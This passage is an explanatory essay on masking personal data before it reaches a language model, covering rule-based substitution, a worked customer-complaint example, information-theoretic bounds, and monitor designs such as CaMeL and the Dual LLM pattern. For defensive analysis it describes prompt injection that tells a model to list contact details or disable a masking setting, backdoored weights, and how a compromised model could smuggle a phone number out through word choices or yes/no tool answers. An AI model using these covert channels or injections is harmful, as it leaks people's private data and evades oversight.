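# Rule-based masking and redaction by a language model: what a compromised model can and cannot undo

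## How sensitive text is masked before a language model reads it

Masking replaces names, account numbers, passwords and similar details in a text with stand-ins, so that the text can go to a reader who should not see those details. Increasingly, that reader is a large language model on another company's servers. When a support desk uses a model to summarise a complaint, or a clinic uses one to draft a letter, the text goes to the model's provider. Yashwant, Sharma and colleagues (2026) point out in *Redacting Personal Data* that copies then remain in provider systems, application logs and the traces that engineers keep for debugging. If the sender masks the text before sending it, all of those copies contain stand-ins instead of the original details.

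Reversible masking is called pseudonymisation in European data protection law. The European Data Protection Board (EDPB, 2025) describes it as replacing personal data with information that does not directly identify anyone. Linking the result back to a person requires additional information, "like a lookup table or a secret key". The protection depends largely on who holds that table or key and whether the model reading the text can access it.

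### One complaint, masked

Suppose a company receives this message and wants a language model to draft a reply:

> Maria Keller (maria.keller@example.org, 555-0142) disputes invoice 88317. Her manager, the only cardiologist in Elmford, agrees.

The company knows who the customer is because the message came in through her account. Its masking program is ordinary code, similar to the program Yashwant and colleagues built for résumés. It uses two regular expressions, which describe the shape of a string, to look for email addresses and phone numbers. The phone pattern has to accept seven digits; the one in the résumé program requires ten and would have missed 555-0142. A separate lookup searches the text for the name on the customer's record, ignoring case, first for the full name and then for its parts.

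These searches collide, since "maria" and "keller" also occur inside the email address. The program sorts its finds by starting position, longer ones first, and skips any that overlaps one it has already taken, so the address goes as a single piece. Each such find is a *sensitive span*, a stretch of text to hide. Each distinct value gets a numbered *placeholder*, and the model receives this:

> [PERSON_1] ([EMAIL_1], [PHONE_1]) disputes invoice 88317. Her manager, the only cardiologist in Elmford, agrees.

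The company keeps the *mapping*, the table that links placeholders to originals:

| Placeholder | Original value | Found by |
|---|---|---|
| [PERSON_1] | Maria Keller | lookup of the known customer |
| [EMAIL_1] | maria.keller@example.org | email pattern |
| [PHONE_1] | 555-0142 | phone pattern |

If the model's draft begins "Dear [PERSON_1], we are looking into invoice 88317", code looks up the placeholder in the table and replaces it with the name, so the customer gets a normal letter.

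The program deliberately leaves the invoice number readable so that the reply can mention it. It also fails to mask the phrase describing the manager, even though it works as designed. The phrase has no fixed format, and the manager is not on the customer's record. Elmford has only one cardiologist, so anyone with a local directory can work out who the phrase refers to. Agyemang, Kponyo and colleagues (2026) call this implicit identity in *LLM-Redactor*, and give the example of a CFO "whose wife works at the competitor".

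### Detect, substitute, restore

The procedure has three steps, and Ma, Wu and Yan (2026), in *BodhiPromptShield*, give a compact notation for them. Let $x$ be the original text and $E(x)$ the list of sensitive spans that the *detector* finds in it, each with a category and a confidence score. Substitution is then an operator

$$T_\pi : (x, E(x)) \mapsto (\tilde{x}, K)$$

where $\pi$ is the masking policy, $\tilde{x}$ the masked text and $K$ the mapping. The model $f$ computes $y = f(\tilde{x})$. *Restoration* takes the model's output and the mapping and produces the final text, $\mathcal{R}_\rho(y, K) \mapsto y'$, under a policy $\rho$ that says where and when real values may return.

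$K$ appears in the substitution and the restoration but not in $f(\tilde{x})$. The *containment argument* is based on this difference. Under this argument, if plain code does the substituting, the harm that even an attacker-controlled model can do to the masked values is bounded, because the model never saw them and cannot write to the table.

Nothing in the notation requires $T$ to be code, though. Hou, Shang and colleagues (2025), in *A General Pseudonymization Framework for Cloud-Based LLMs*, cut substitution in two, first choosing a replacement and then putting it in, and tried both code and models for the parts. Adding the options for restoration gives four jobs, each of which can go either way:

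| Job | Done by code | Done by a model |
|---|---|---|
| Detect the spans | patterns, dictionaries, lookup of known names | a trained name recogniser, or a language model that lists names |
| Choose a replacement | a counter, or a random draw from values of the same kind | a language model invents one |
| Put it in | overwrite the span and leave the rest alone | a language model writes the text out again |
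| Restore | look up the placeholder, or decrypt it with a key | a small local model edits the answer |

Code that restores masked values by lookup can be very simple. Agyemang and colleagues keep the mapping in the memory of one running process, match placeholders exactly, and delete the table after each request. If the process crashes, nobody can unmask the answer, which they consider the right way to fail. *PromptGraph* (2026) adds consistency checks and leaves a placeholder unresolved if the model has rewritten it or made it up. Small local models can also restore the private values, as in Hide and Seek, an earlier system that Beskorovainyi (2026) mentions in *Reversible Pseudonymisation of Documents Sent to External LLMs*.

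### From hospital records to language models

Most of the methods in the code column are older than language models and come from medicine. Latanya Sweeney's Scrub system, which *Leveraging text skeleton for de-identification of electronic medical records* dates to early 1996, used templates and look-up tables to hide identifiers in medical records. That same year the United States passed HIPAA, the health privacy law behind the list of 18 kinds of identifier that de-identified records must not contain. Neamatullah, Douglass and colleagues (2008), in *Automated de-identification of free-text medical records*, wrote a Perl program that searched nursing notes using regular expressions, dictionaries and the names of the hospital's actual patients, the same method that catches "Maria Keller". When Meystre, Friedlin and colleagues (2010) reviewed 18 such systems in *Automatic de-identification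 of textual documents in the electronic health record*, most still used only patterns, rules and dictionaries, which typically took experts months to build by hand. The more recent systems trained classifiers on annotated records to label each word as identifying or harmless. Neural name recognisers followed, and free software libraries such as spaCy and Presidio made them easy to install.

Language models are the newest tools for masking sensitive text. *Benchmarking transformer-based models for medical record de-identification* (Kuo, Soltan and colleagues, 2025) compared five of them with four specialised tools on 3,650 records from a group of UK hospitals. GPT-4 came close to the best specialised tool. The smaller models redacted diagnoses, and one of them, Gemma-7b, invented details, including a "prior trauma-related injury sustained one month back". Regular expressions don't make this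 second kind of error, though they can miss names.

### Where the model sits

So a language model can occupy quite different places in a masking system, and an attacker who controls it gains different things in each.

A language model can propose the spans to redact. *RedactionBench* (2026) tests commercial models by requiring each one to list every string to redact, word for word, in a single tool call. The benchmark's own code intercepts the list and makes the replacements. A model in this role reads the original text, and a bad list leaves sensitive spans in place or removes harmless ones, but the output contains only original text and the fixed word "REDACTED".

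A language model can write the redacted text itself, which is called *generative redaction*. *Domain Agnostic Text Redaction from Natural Language Rules using Instruction Tuning* (2026) fine-tunes Microsoft's Phi-3.5 to do this. The model receives a document and a redaction rule in plain language, and its training target includes a list of sensitive spans, an explanation and the finished redacted text. Because the model writes that finished text, it could change an amount or copy Keller's phone number into a new sentence, and only a further check could catch the error. Such checks tend to look for other problems. In the rephrasing option that Agyemang and colleagues tested, a validator rejects the rewrite when fewer than 70% of the key technical terms survive, which guards against lost content but not leaked content. Roy Chowdhury, Glukhov and colleagues (2026) write in *Prϵϵmpt* that rephrasing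 by a language model "lacks formal guarantees".

Some designs split masking between a detector and a language model. *Residual Attribute Leakage Is an Interface* (2026) runs one such system, INTACT, in which the detector selects the spans to mask and the language model replaces each with a vaguer but truthful description, so "Maria Keller" might become "a customer". The paper also reports a test in which a rewriting model received documents that already contained placeholders. The model altered at least one placeholder in 16.5% of the court judgments and 10.4% of the medical questions it handled. An altered placeholder may no longer match any entry in the mapping used to restore the original text, so even a rewrite by an uncompromised model can prevent restoration.

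Alternatively, the model can receive only the masked text, like the one drafting the reply to Keller. Companies already sell this arrangement. Salesforce's *Explore Large Language Model Data Masking* describes a layer that finds names with patterns and machine learning, replaces "Jim" with `<Person_0>`, sends the prompt to the model, and restores the name in the response.

Masking sensitive text before a model reads it provides substantial protection, judging by *Inadvertent Context Leakage in Language Models* (2026). Even when a model correctly refuses to reveal a secret in its context, its harmless answers carry some information about the secret's value. An adversary trained with reinforcement learning used this leakage to extract full Social Security numbers from agents running on Claude Opus 4.6 and Gemini 3.1 Pro. Replacing a secret with a placeholder therefore protects it much better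 than telling the model not to reveal it. Models that propose spans to mask and models that rewrite the text both carry this risk if an attacker can query them or read their output.

One system can have models in several of these places. Agyemang and colleagues trust a small local model to detect and rephrase sensitive text, and distrust the cloud model that answers the request. An argument that the cloud model is contained does not apply to the local model, which reads every original value.

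### Two meanings of "deterministic"

People who build masking systems often call them deterministic, and the word has two meanings that are easy to run together.

One meaning of "deterministic" masking is that no part of the output is sampled from a model. This is *rule-based substitution*. *PerceptFence* (2026), a filter for AI assistants that watch a user's screen, calls the boundary it guards deterministic because its redaction engine is "not model-based". Strange spelling may hide a value from the detector, but an instruction in the text has no effect on the code that replaces values. A trained name recogniser can run before that code, and the substitution is still rule-based, because the recogniser only labels stretches of text, sometimes wrongly, and doesn't generate any of the output.

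"Deterministic" can also mean that the same value always gets the same stand-in. *Deploying Pseudonymisation Techniques* (2022), a guide from ENISA, the EU's cybersecurity agency, defines deterministic pseudonymisation this way. It distinguishes this from document-randomised pseudonymisation, where the stand-in repeats only within a consistent scope, and fully randomised pseudonymisation, where the stand-in is designed never to repeat. In these terms, the Keller program is document-randomised if its counter restarts with each message, because Keller is [PERSON_1] throughout her complaint but the same label refers to someone else in the next one.

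Repeatable redaction decisions and consistent replacements are separate properties of a masking system. *Morpheus* (2026), which masks Greek clinical notes, makes the same redaction decisions on every run but chooses new *surrogates* each time (realistic placeholders, such as invented names). A language model told to use one replacement per person throughout a text might comply, but it would still generate every word of the result.

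*Anonymization of Portuguese Clinical Notes Using Large Language Models* ran two Llama models at a low temperature with the random seed fixed at 42. These settings make a run easier to repeat, but the models still produced the text after reading the original notes. If a planted instruction worked on such a setup, it would probably work again on the next run.

The containment argument requires only that there be no sampled text. Whether placeholders repeat affects other things, such as how easily an observer can link two documents about the same person.

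### What makes a model compromised

A *compromised model* is one whose output an attacker controls or steers. The safest assumption for the containment argument is that the attacker chooses every word. An attacker can gain some of this control through the text the model reads, through its weights, or by running the service.

The easiest route is *prompt injection*. An attacker plants instructions in text that the model reads, to make it act for them. Willison (2026) uses the term only when the model follows the planted instructions, not when an agent merely runs into a trap set in its environment. In the running example, somebody could add a line to the complaint telling the model to list every contact detail it can find. The attacker can steer the model only where it reads the planted text. They can't directly see what the model reads or writes, so they have to get its output sent somewhere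 they can read it.

An attacker who alters a model's weights acts before anyone deploys it and may never touch a conversation. The tampering can affect every answer, or only answers to prompts that contain a trigger. The security organisation OWASP has separate entries for *supply chain* and *poisoning* in its 2025 risk list. *LLM Safety and Guardrails*, an online handbook page, puts backdoored weights under the first and training-time attacks under the second. This attacker also sees nothing unless the model's output reaches them. A downloaded local model that detects sensitive text carries the same risk, and its prompt contains Keller's real phone number.

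A hostile provider sees every masked prompt from every session, can store and compare them, and can return any text as the model's answer. Published designs usually assume a less hostile one. *Veil-Then-Reveal* (Elmahallawy, Shaaban and Carroll, 2026), which keeps the keys and mapping on the user's device, assumes an "honest-but-curious" provider that may log and correlate everything but performs inference correctly. Agyemang and colleagues assume a vendor that is "curious but not actively malicious". Such a provider reads $\tilde{x}$ but does not tamper with $y$. Security against it therefore doesn't establish security against a provider that can choose the $y$ that the restoration code processes.

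Theft of the mapping is a separate threat. Ma and colleagues list an adversary who targets the table and the restoration credentials, but they treat a full compromise of the table as a deployment failure that their prototype cannot withstand. The containment argument must exclude this case too. It assumes that the detector's host, the substitution and restoration programs, and the storage for $K$ are *trusted code*, meaning that they are correct and the model cannot reach them. An attacker who has broken into those components can read Keller's number directly from the table without using a model.

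## The argument: what a model can and cannot do to an existing mapping

The containment argument makes two claims about the system that drafts the reply to Maria Keller. The integrity claim is that nothing the model writes can change the table $K$, in which the code linked [PERSON_1] to her name. The confidentiality claim is that the model's output carries no more information about her hidden details than the visible part of her complaint does. Both claims apply to any model, even one whose output an attacker chooses word by word. Whether they hold depends on how the company connects the parts of its system.

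### Why the table stays the same

The masking program takes the original text $x$, the policy $\pi$ and, if it picks placeholders at random, random numbers $R$. It uses these to write the table $K$ and the masked text before it calls the model. When the draft comes back, the restoration code looks up each placeholder in $K$, which it never changes, and fills in the letter.

The model's output is not an input to $K$, and this alone proves integrity. If the company replaced the model with another one, or with an attacker at a keyboard, $K$ would be identical character for character. This holds regardless of the model's training, honesty or skill.

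In a longer conversation, the claim holds only for existing rows, and only if the program never overwrites or removes them. If Keller writes again, or if the model asks for a document, the program masks the new text and adds rows to the table. The model may have chosen that document, so it can influence the new rows. It could also change old rows if the counter restarted with every message while the table carried over. An attacker could then get the model to request a web page about a Victor Lang, the program would file him under [PERSON_1], and the letter to Keller would open "Dear Victor Lang". The attacker would have changed a row even though only trusted code wrote to the table.

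### Why the model learns only what the surrounding text gives away

Let $S$ be the hidden values, here the name, the email address and the phone number. Let $C$ be what remains of the complaint after the code cuts them out, plus a type label for each gap and a note of which gaps held the same value. Let $M$ be the masked text the model receives (written $\tilde{x}$ earlier), and let $Y$ be the model's output. The mutual information $I(S;Y)$ measures, in bits, how much seeing $Y$ reduces a reader's uncertainty about $S$ on average. It is zero if $Y$ doesn't help a reader guess $S$.

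The code builds $M$ by writing a placeholder into each gap of $C$, using a counter or the random numbers $R$. Assume that $R$ is independent of both $S$ and $C$. Somebody who already has $C$ then learns nothing more about $S$ from $M$, which means that $I(S;M \mid C) = 0$. The information that $C$ and $M$ jointly carry about $S$ splits in two ways:

$$I(S;C,M) = I(S;C) + \underbrace{I(S;M \mid C)}_{=\,0} = I(S;M) + I(S;C \mid M)$$

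The last term is never negative, so $I(S;M) \le I(S;C)$. The model computes $Y$ from $M$ and its own sampling noise, and the same step applied to $M$ and $Y$ gives the full chain:

$$I(S;Y) \le I(S;M) \le I(S;C)$$

This is the data-processing inequality. Processing a text can lose information about $S$ but cannot add any. If the placeholders come from a counter, $M$ and $C$ determine each other, and the right-hand inequality becomes an equality. The placeholders then add no information about $S$, and any leak comes from the ordinary words around them.

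The words "her manager" in Keller's complaint leak that the customer is a woman, which is at most one bit of information. She reports to a cardiologist in Elmford, so she probably works at a medical practice there, which would narrow her name to a short staff list. Her seven-digit phone number has ten million possible values, or about 23 bits. If nothing in the text bears on the number, the model's best guess has about a one in ten million chance of being right. A more capable model can get closer to the bound $I(S;C)$ but can't exceed it.

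The bound is weaker than it may look, partly because it depends on what the reader already knows. Someone with the company's ledger can identify Keller from invoice 88317 alone. Given that background knowledge, $A$, the inequality still holds as $I(S;Y \mid A) \le I(S;C \mid A)$, but the right-hand side now includes her whole name. The bound is also an average, so a figure of 0.1 bits could mean that one complaint in a hundred reveals ten bits and the rest reveal none.

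$S$ contains only the values that the code replaced. Elmahallawy and colleagues limit their guarantee to detected values and exclude inference from context. In their tests, the program detected 97.9% of the personal details and protected 95.2% of those it detected. Values that it detects but leaves in place, such as the partial date "20th September", belong to $C$. *SurrogateShield* (2026), another masker that runs on the user's side, goes further and calls it an "unconditional" invariant that no real personal data reaches the provider. But its detector has an F1 score of 98.87%, a combined measure of misses and false alarms on which a perfect detector would get 100%, so the invariant can hold only for the values that the detector finds.

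Ma and colleagues decline to give a bound for their own system. They note that even a randomised replacement layer would not cover the untouched context. This is consistent with the inequality, since $I(S;C)$ is the part that masking leaves unchanged.

### What has to hold, and what happens to Keller when it doesn't

The derivation relies on four facts about the system. Every input passes through the masker, the model has no other route to $S$, the code is correct, and the model cannot change the code or its configuration.

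Suppose Keller attaches a photo of the invoice showing her name and phone number, and the support software forwards attachments straight to the model. Even if the program masks her message perfectly, the model still receives those details in the photo. Whether inputs can bypass the masker often depends on how a developer installs it. Agyemang and colleagues offer their redactor both as a proxy that all calls to the cloud model pass through and as a set of tools that an agent can call. With the tools alone, masking happens only when the agent calls them. Earlier turns of a conversation also need masking, because a chat program usually resends them with every request. *SurrogateShield* handles this by keeping only surrogates in the stored history.

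A model can also reach $S$ without reading the original message. It may have a memory note linking invoice 88317 to Keller, written last week when somebody had switched masking off. Keller may have posted the same complaint under her own name on a public forum, and the post may have ended up in the training data. The model may also have a harmless-looking tool that compares a hidden number with a given one, which lets it check whether [PHONE_1] is below 500-0000. No masker would redact the tool's yes-or-no answers, but 24 of them are enough to identify any seven-digit number.

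Restoration can also open such a route if real values return while the model is still working. When Ma and colleagues restored values during the planning stage, 51.0% of the protected values were readable in the text released to the agent. Waiting until the authorised final step reduced this to 1.6%.

Even a small code error can expose personal data to the model. If a programmer reversed the rule that longer finds go first, the program would take "maria" first, skip the full address because it overlaps, and then take "keller". The model would receive two name placeholders with a dot between them, followed by "@example.org", which would reveal her email domain and the format of her address. A badly written error handler could expose far more by copying the whole table into an error message that goes to the model.

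Finally, suppose the assistant can edit the file that holds the masker's settings. A line planted in a complaint tells it to fix a formatting problem by turning off the phone pattern. Keller's existing row is unchanged, but the next customer's number is sent unmasked. Agyemang and colleagues' proxy depends on a similar setting, an environment variable that directs the agent's calls to the redactor. An agent able to change its own environment could direct them back to the provider. *aiAuthZ* (2026) describes a gateway that authorises AI agents' actions and treats the model as "an untrusted emitter of requests". To guard against tampering, the gateway and its databases run on machines for which the agent has no credentials.

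### What a compromised model can still do

If all four conditions hold, an attacker who controls the model has only the powers in the middle column. The right-hand column is for a model that does generative redaction.

| Power | Model that reads only masked text | Model that writes the redaction |
|---|---|---|
| Read a stored value | No | Yes, in the original text |
| Rewrite an existing row of $K$ | No | No, but it can supply false new rows if code builds $K$ from its output |
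| Turn a placeholder back into its value | No | It has no need to |
| Read a span that the detector missed | Yes | Yes |
| Guess a value from context | Yes, within the bound $I(S;C)$ | It has no need to |
| Drop, repeat, swap or invent placeholders | Yes | Yes |
| Influence which new text the system fetches and masks later | Yes, if it can request documents | Yes, if it can request documents |
| Smuggle a hidden value out in its own words | No, beyond what it can guess | Yes |

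A compromised model can still do harm. It can swap placeholders so that a real value is shown to someone who shouldn't see it. It can also invent placeholders, which is dangerous if the attacker can guess which ones exist. If the model can request documents, it can test the detector, for example by requesting a page that spells a phone number in ten odd ways and checking which spellings come back readable.

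Still, the two columns describe very different situations. A model that writes the redaction reads $x$, which contains $S$, so the only limit on $I(S;Y)$ is the entire uncertainty about $S$, which gives no protection. Filtering the model's output doesn't restore the bound. A filter can search for the digits 555-0142, but a compromised model can encode them in its wording and punctuation instead. With 24 choices between "and" and "as well as", or between a comma and none, it can encode any seven-digit number in a text that looks perfectly redacted.

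A model that only proposes spans is in between: it can't compose sentences, but it can leave Keller's number off its list.

An uncompromised model would usually redact correctly, but *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) explains why this is a poor basis for security. If a component refuses improper access 99% of the time, an attacker can look for the remaining 1%, and there are search and optimisation methods for finding it in language models.

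### The reference monitor

The idea of limiting what a program can reach, whatever it was written to do, is more than fifty years old. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) reported to the US Air Force on how users with different security clearances could share one computer. The panel behind the report assumed that some users would write hostile programs. It proposed a *reference monitor*, which checks every attempt by a program to reach data, another program or a device against a list of what the program's user may do. Anderson drew the permissions as a matrix, with users and programs as rows and the things they might reach as columns. In a matrix for Keller's system, the cell in the model's row and the column for $K$ would be empty, because the model has no permission to reach $K$.

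Anderson set three requirements for the mechanism. It must be tamper-proof, or an attacker would alter it. The system must always invoke it, because any program that escapes the check becomes part of the security apparatus and has to meet the same standard. And it must be small enough to analyze and test completely, or nobody can know that it works. The commercial operating systems of the day did not meet these requirements. GCOS III, for example, had 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, and most of it ran with the memory checks suspended.

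Three of the four conditions for masking correspond to these requirements: the masker must see every input, the model must not be able to alter the masker, and the masker's code must be small enough to be verified as correct. The remaining condition, that the model has no other route to $S$, is harder to meet now than in 1972, because a language model may already contain memorised copies of other people's files, unlike a hostile program on an Air Force computer at that time.

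Seeing every input has also become harder. Christodorescu and colleagues observe that agents often lack a clean boundary where a rule can be enforced. A browser agent, for example, works through clicks and keystrokes, and a policy written in terms of clicks makes little sense. Such an agent is a problem for masking because the whole screen is an input, including any customer's name on it.

### Controllers that fill in variables

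*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) applies a similar separation to language models. It addresses the risk that a malicious message could take over an assistant that both reads and sends email. The design uses a privileged model, which takes the user's instructions and can use tools but never reads untrusted text, and a quarantined model, which reads the untrusted text and has no tools. The controller between them is "regular software, not a language model".

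If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the privileged model instructs the controller to fetch the email and store it as $VAR1. It then requests a summary of $VAR1, and the controller passes the actual email to the quarantined model and stores the result as $VAR2. The privileged model instructs the controller to display $VAR2 without having read the email or the summary. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) calls the controller an orchestrator and adds that the privileged model must be unable to look up a variable's content.

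$VAR1 works much like [PERSON_1]. In both designs, code keeps a table of placeholders and their contents, and the model handles only the placeholders. Willison's design keeps hostile text from the model to protect its decisions, whereas masking keeps private values from the model to protect the values. The drafting model in Keller's case still reads what she wrote, so masking does not stop her message from taking control of the model.

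Willison called the solution "pretty bad" and worried mainly about its complexity, since a single mistake that lets untrusted text through to the privileged model would waste all the effort. Even when the code is right, an injected instruction can corrupt the content of a variable, though it can't add a new action. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example of an assistant that sends today's schedule to the user's boss. A planted calendar entry can change the email's text but not its recipient, which the plan fixes.

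Google DeepMind published a system called CaMeL in 2025, which Willison considers a fix for a flaw in the earlier pattern. He says it turns the user's request into steps in a Python-like language and checks each step's inputs and outputs. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) describes the main addition, an interpreter that tracks where each piece of data came from and applies security policies before every tool call. If planted text replaces the real recipient's address with the attacker's, the interpreter can block the message because the address came from an untrusted source.

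### What the machine-checked proofs establish

Researchers have since stated such guarantees precisely enough for proof-checking software to verify them. The three results below concern agents in general, not masking, but each covers a wide range of model behaviour and depends on assumptions about the surrounding system.

The simplest is close to the integrity claim. David, Guarnieri and Gervais (2026), in *Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems*, consider agents that test websites for security holes. A contract $C$ (unrelated to the remaining text above) lists the permitted targets, actions, budgets and recipients of reports, and a monitor checks every proposed action against it. For every finite sequence $P$ of proposed actions, those that the monitor lets through satisfy the contract:

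$$\mathrm{Run}_C(P) \models C$$

The proof considers one action at a time. A refused action adds nothing to the record, and an admitted one complied with the contract when the monitor admitted it. As with the mapping, the argument does not depend on the model's behaviour. If the contract forbade the agent to write to the file holding $K$, much of the integrity claim would follow as a special case. The theorem requires every action to pass through the monitor before it takes effect, so it does not apply if a tool bypasses the monitor.

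In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) prove a result closer to the confidentiality claim. Their LLMbda calculus is a small programming language for agents in which every value carries a label, such as secret or untrusted, and every operation passes the labels on. The main theorem is a form of *noninterference*, meaning that changing the secret inputs cannot change what an observer without access to secrets sees, apart from whether the program finishes. Because language models sample their answers, the theorem is stated in terms of the probabilities of outcomes. The proof, checked in Lean, covers the interpreter that actually runs the agent and calls the model. On the banking tasks of AgentDojo, a prompt-injection benchmark, an agent written in this language resisted the attack in all but two of 1,296 runs. It was about as useful as CaMeL with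 its policy checks off, and turning them on halves CaMeL's usefulness.

Garby and colleagues also found two leaks in CaMeL that are relevant to anyone writing a masker. In the first, a variable starts as true and the program sets it to false only if an account balance is low. When the balance is high, the program skips that line, so CaMeL never marks the variable as secret. An email that goes out only if the variable is true then reveals that the balance is high. The second leak is an accidental version of the yes-or-no phone tool. CaMeL's interpreter runs inside an ordinary retry loop that nobody tracks. Each attempt reveals one bit about the secret, depending on whether the policy blocks it, and an attacker can use the loop to collect these bits until they have the whole secret.

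*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) starts from the objection that noninterference is too strict, since an assistant that answers meeting requests is supposed to reveal its owner's calendar. The paper compares the real agent with a reference agent that runs the same plan under the same monitor but never follows planted instructions. The real agent is *relatively secure* if, whenever an attacker can use injection to tell two secrets apart, some input to the reference agent also distinguishes them. Under this definition, the agent may reveal the calendar but may not add a password reset code to the reply.

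A fence is a monitor that withdraws tools when the agent first reads untrusted content. The central result is that if the fence permanently withdraws every tool an injection could call, the agent is relatively secure for every plan. The result assumes that each planted instruction the model obeys triggers only one tool call, and that when it obeys is fixed before the run starts. The model may otherwise behave in any way. The result therefore does not cover a model that uses a secret to decide when to obey. A properly masked model could not use Keller's phone number this way, because it never receives the number.

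Dongol finds that the dual-model pattern leaks when the data has no labels, because the quarantined model can quote the user's private notes in an answer that the plan then sends out. With CaMeL-style labels, the pattern is secure however the quarantined model behaves, but the monitor blocks even the honest reply. The pattern leaks again if the plan sends a harmless 1 or 0 depending on the quarantined model's answer, since the choice between them can depend on the notes. All three cases involve a model that reads the private material, as a generative redactor does, whereas the model drafting Keller's letter has no private material to quote.

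These theorems apply only to systems that satisfy seven assumptions. The right-hand column translates each into the complaint system.

| Assumption | What Dongol requires | Counterpart for Keller's complaint |
|---|---|---|
| Trusted execution | A trusted interpreter runs the plan, and the model can't skip steps | Masking finishes before any text leaves |
| Complete mediation | The model reaches tools and untrusted sources only through the monitor | No attachment or database answer goes around the masker |
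| Mediated reads | Untrusted content enters the context only after the monitor allows it | The program masks a fetched page before the model sees it |
| Silent denials | A refused request has no effect that the attacker can see | Error messages reveal nothing about the real values |
| Limited observation | The attacker sees neither the monitor's state nor the agent's internal steps | Displaying the finished letter doesn't load an image from the attacker's server |
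| Fresh sessions | A new session clears everything the model retained from untrusted content | No memory note survives from an unmasked conversation |
| Trusted channels | The attacker can't write to the sources of trusted inputs | Nobody can blank the customer record that supplies the name to search for |

The last row is easy to overlook. The masker finds "Maria Keller" because her name is on record, so an attacker who can edit the record can keep her name from being masked in her next message, without access to the model or the code.

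Dongol's framework does not cover side channels, poisoned tools or errors by the planner. It also excludes tools whose reply depends on the call, such as a search engine that the attacker runs.

### Whether the trust has only moved

One could object that this only shifts trust from the model to the code. David and colleagues agree that trust moves from learned components to "a small, auditable enforcement barrier", and they say users must still rely on the monitor, the points where it intercepts actions, and the contract itself. A Lean proof doesn't establish that a deployed system matches the definitions in the proof.

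The objection has substance, because CaMeL leaked where its tracked part met ordinary Python, even though competent people designed it specifically to control information flow. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) attributes some of the difficulty to the language. CaMeL's plans use a restricted form of Python that still has features such as dynamic typing and reflection, which make the code hard to analyse and prevent strong guarantees. The paper recommends a purpose-built language with bounded loops and simple conditionals. Anderson had a more basic concern, that someone could hide a "trap door" in the trusted software while writing or maintaining it. Masking products have also had faults of their own.

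Even so, trusting the masking program instead of the model helps a good deal here, because the program is much simpler than CaMeL's interpreter. It makes one pass over the text, fills one table and later looks up exact matches. It doesn't run programs that a model wrote, and its behaviour never has to depend on what Keller's phone number is. A programmer can read the substitution code in an afternoon and test it on awkward cases, whereas Christodorescu and colleagues doubt that anyone can build provable defences on a component as unpredictable as a language model.

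Proofs are also becoming easier to produce. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, helped generate the theorems and proofs in Dongol's development, which runs to about 31,600 lines. The proof assistant Isabelle checked every proof, so nobody had to trust the model that helped write them. The containment argument applies here too, because a reliable checker verifies the work of an unreliable writer.

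Good design can also limit the damage when trusted code fails. Ma and colleagues simulated an attacker with increasing access to their mapping. Neither the placeholders alone nor a leaked audit log revealed any values. Reading half of one session's table revealed only that half. A stolen session credential exposed all of that session but no others, and only the master secret exposed everything. They tested a reference design, not a live system, but the results show that trusting the code doesn't have to mean that one leaked table exposes every customer's data.

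The detector is harder to trust than the substitution code. A programmer can specify that correct substitution replaces the given spans, records them and changes nothing else. Nobody has a comparable specification of which spans are sensitive, so nobody can prove a detector correct. If the detector is a trained recogniser, it is also far too large to meet Anderson's third requirement. Even if the substitution code is flawless, the model still receives any sensitive detail the detector misses, such as the fact that Keller's manager is the only cardiologist in Elmford.

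## How placeholders are made, and when they can be reversed

After the detector marks a span, the code replaces it with a placeholder. The confidentiality derivation rests on the assumption that the placeholder comes from a counter or random numbers, so that only the table connects it to the hidden value. Many systems instead compute the placeholder by hashing or encrypting the value, often so that they can restore values without a table. It may then be possible to recover the value from the placeholder, and who can do so depends on how the placeholder was computed.

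### Labels and random tokens

A numbered label such as [PHONE_1] shows the type of value removed, its approximate order in the text, and which placeholders replaced the same value. The label doesn't depend on the digits, so nobody can compute 555-0142 from it without the table that matches labels to values.

There is little evidence on how much a placeholder's type helps an attacker. Agyemang and colleagues include the use of type labels among six attack scenarios, because typed placeholders reveal structure. *SurrogateShield* reports a test with a simulated attacker who knew that a masker had run and which types it replaced. The attacker recovered 3 of 196 values behind type labels (one person and two places) and none behind invented values. If both methods protected equally well, all three recoveries would still be from type labels about one time in eight, so the test can't really show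 that one method protects better.

A random token can leave the type out. Ma and colleagues use tokens of the form BPSMAP-{nonce}-{ctr}, where nonce is a random string for the session and ctr is a counter. *PromptGraph* also keeps the type in its private table and sends only an identifier. The model then has to infer from the sentence that a token stands for a phone number.

Both constructions need a table that holds the right value, which is harder to achieve in some languages than in English. Russian surnames, for example, change their endings with grammatical case, so the code has to produce the form that the new sentence requires. Beskorovainyi's masker restored at least 99% of its placeholders in UK English but only 94.6% of name placeholders in Russian, mainly because its inflection code produced wrong surname forms.

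### Hashes

A cryptographic hash function turns any text into a fixed-length string that looks random. The same input always gives the same output, and nobody knows a practical way to run the function backwards. A masker could therefore replace a phone number with its hash and get a consistent placeholder without looking anything up.

The trouble is that an attacker can run the function forwards. There are $10^{10}$ ten-digit phone numbers. An attacker who computes $10^9$ hashes a second and compares each with the placeholder needs at most

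$$\frac{10^{10}}{10^{9}\ \text{per second}} = 10\ \text{seconds}$$

to find the number, and five seconds on average. Keller's seven-digit number takes a hundredth of a second. A random token gives the attacker nothing to test, since every phone number fits it equally well and a faster computer doesn't help.

Hashed names are just as easy to recover. The name lists that Elmahallawy and colleagues use for their surrogates contain 5,719 given names and 6,337 surnames. These make about 36 million full names, which take less than a twentieth of a second to hash. The protection depends on the number of plausible values, which is small for most personal details. A randomly generated 128-bit access key is safe from this attack because there are too many possible keys to try.

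*Pseudonymisation Techniques and Best Practices* (2019), an earlier ENISA guide, lists brute force, dictionary search and guesswork as the main attacks. In *On overview of existing pseudonymisation techniques*, Drogkaris (2021) put an exclamation mark next to plain hashes in a list of methods. In the derivation's terms, a plain hash adds information about $S$ to the masked text that the surrounding words $C$ do not carry, so the bound $I(S;C)$ no longer holds.

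A keyed hash, such as HMAC, mixes a secret key into the computation. The attacker can't test a guess without the key, and a 256-bit key is too long to find by search. This is a weaker kind of guarantee than random tokens give, because it assumes the attacker's computing power is limited, but the difference hardly matters in practice while the key stays secret. If the key leaks, the ten-second attack works again. The company can't reverse a keyed hash either, so it still needs a table to restore the original values.

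### Encryption that keeps the format

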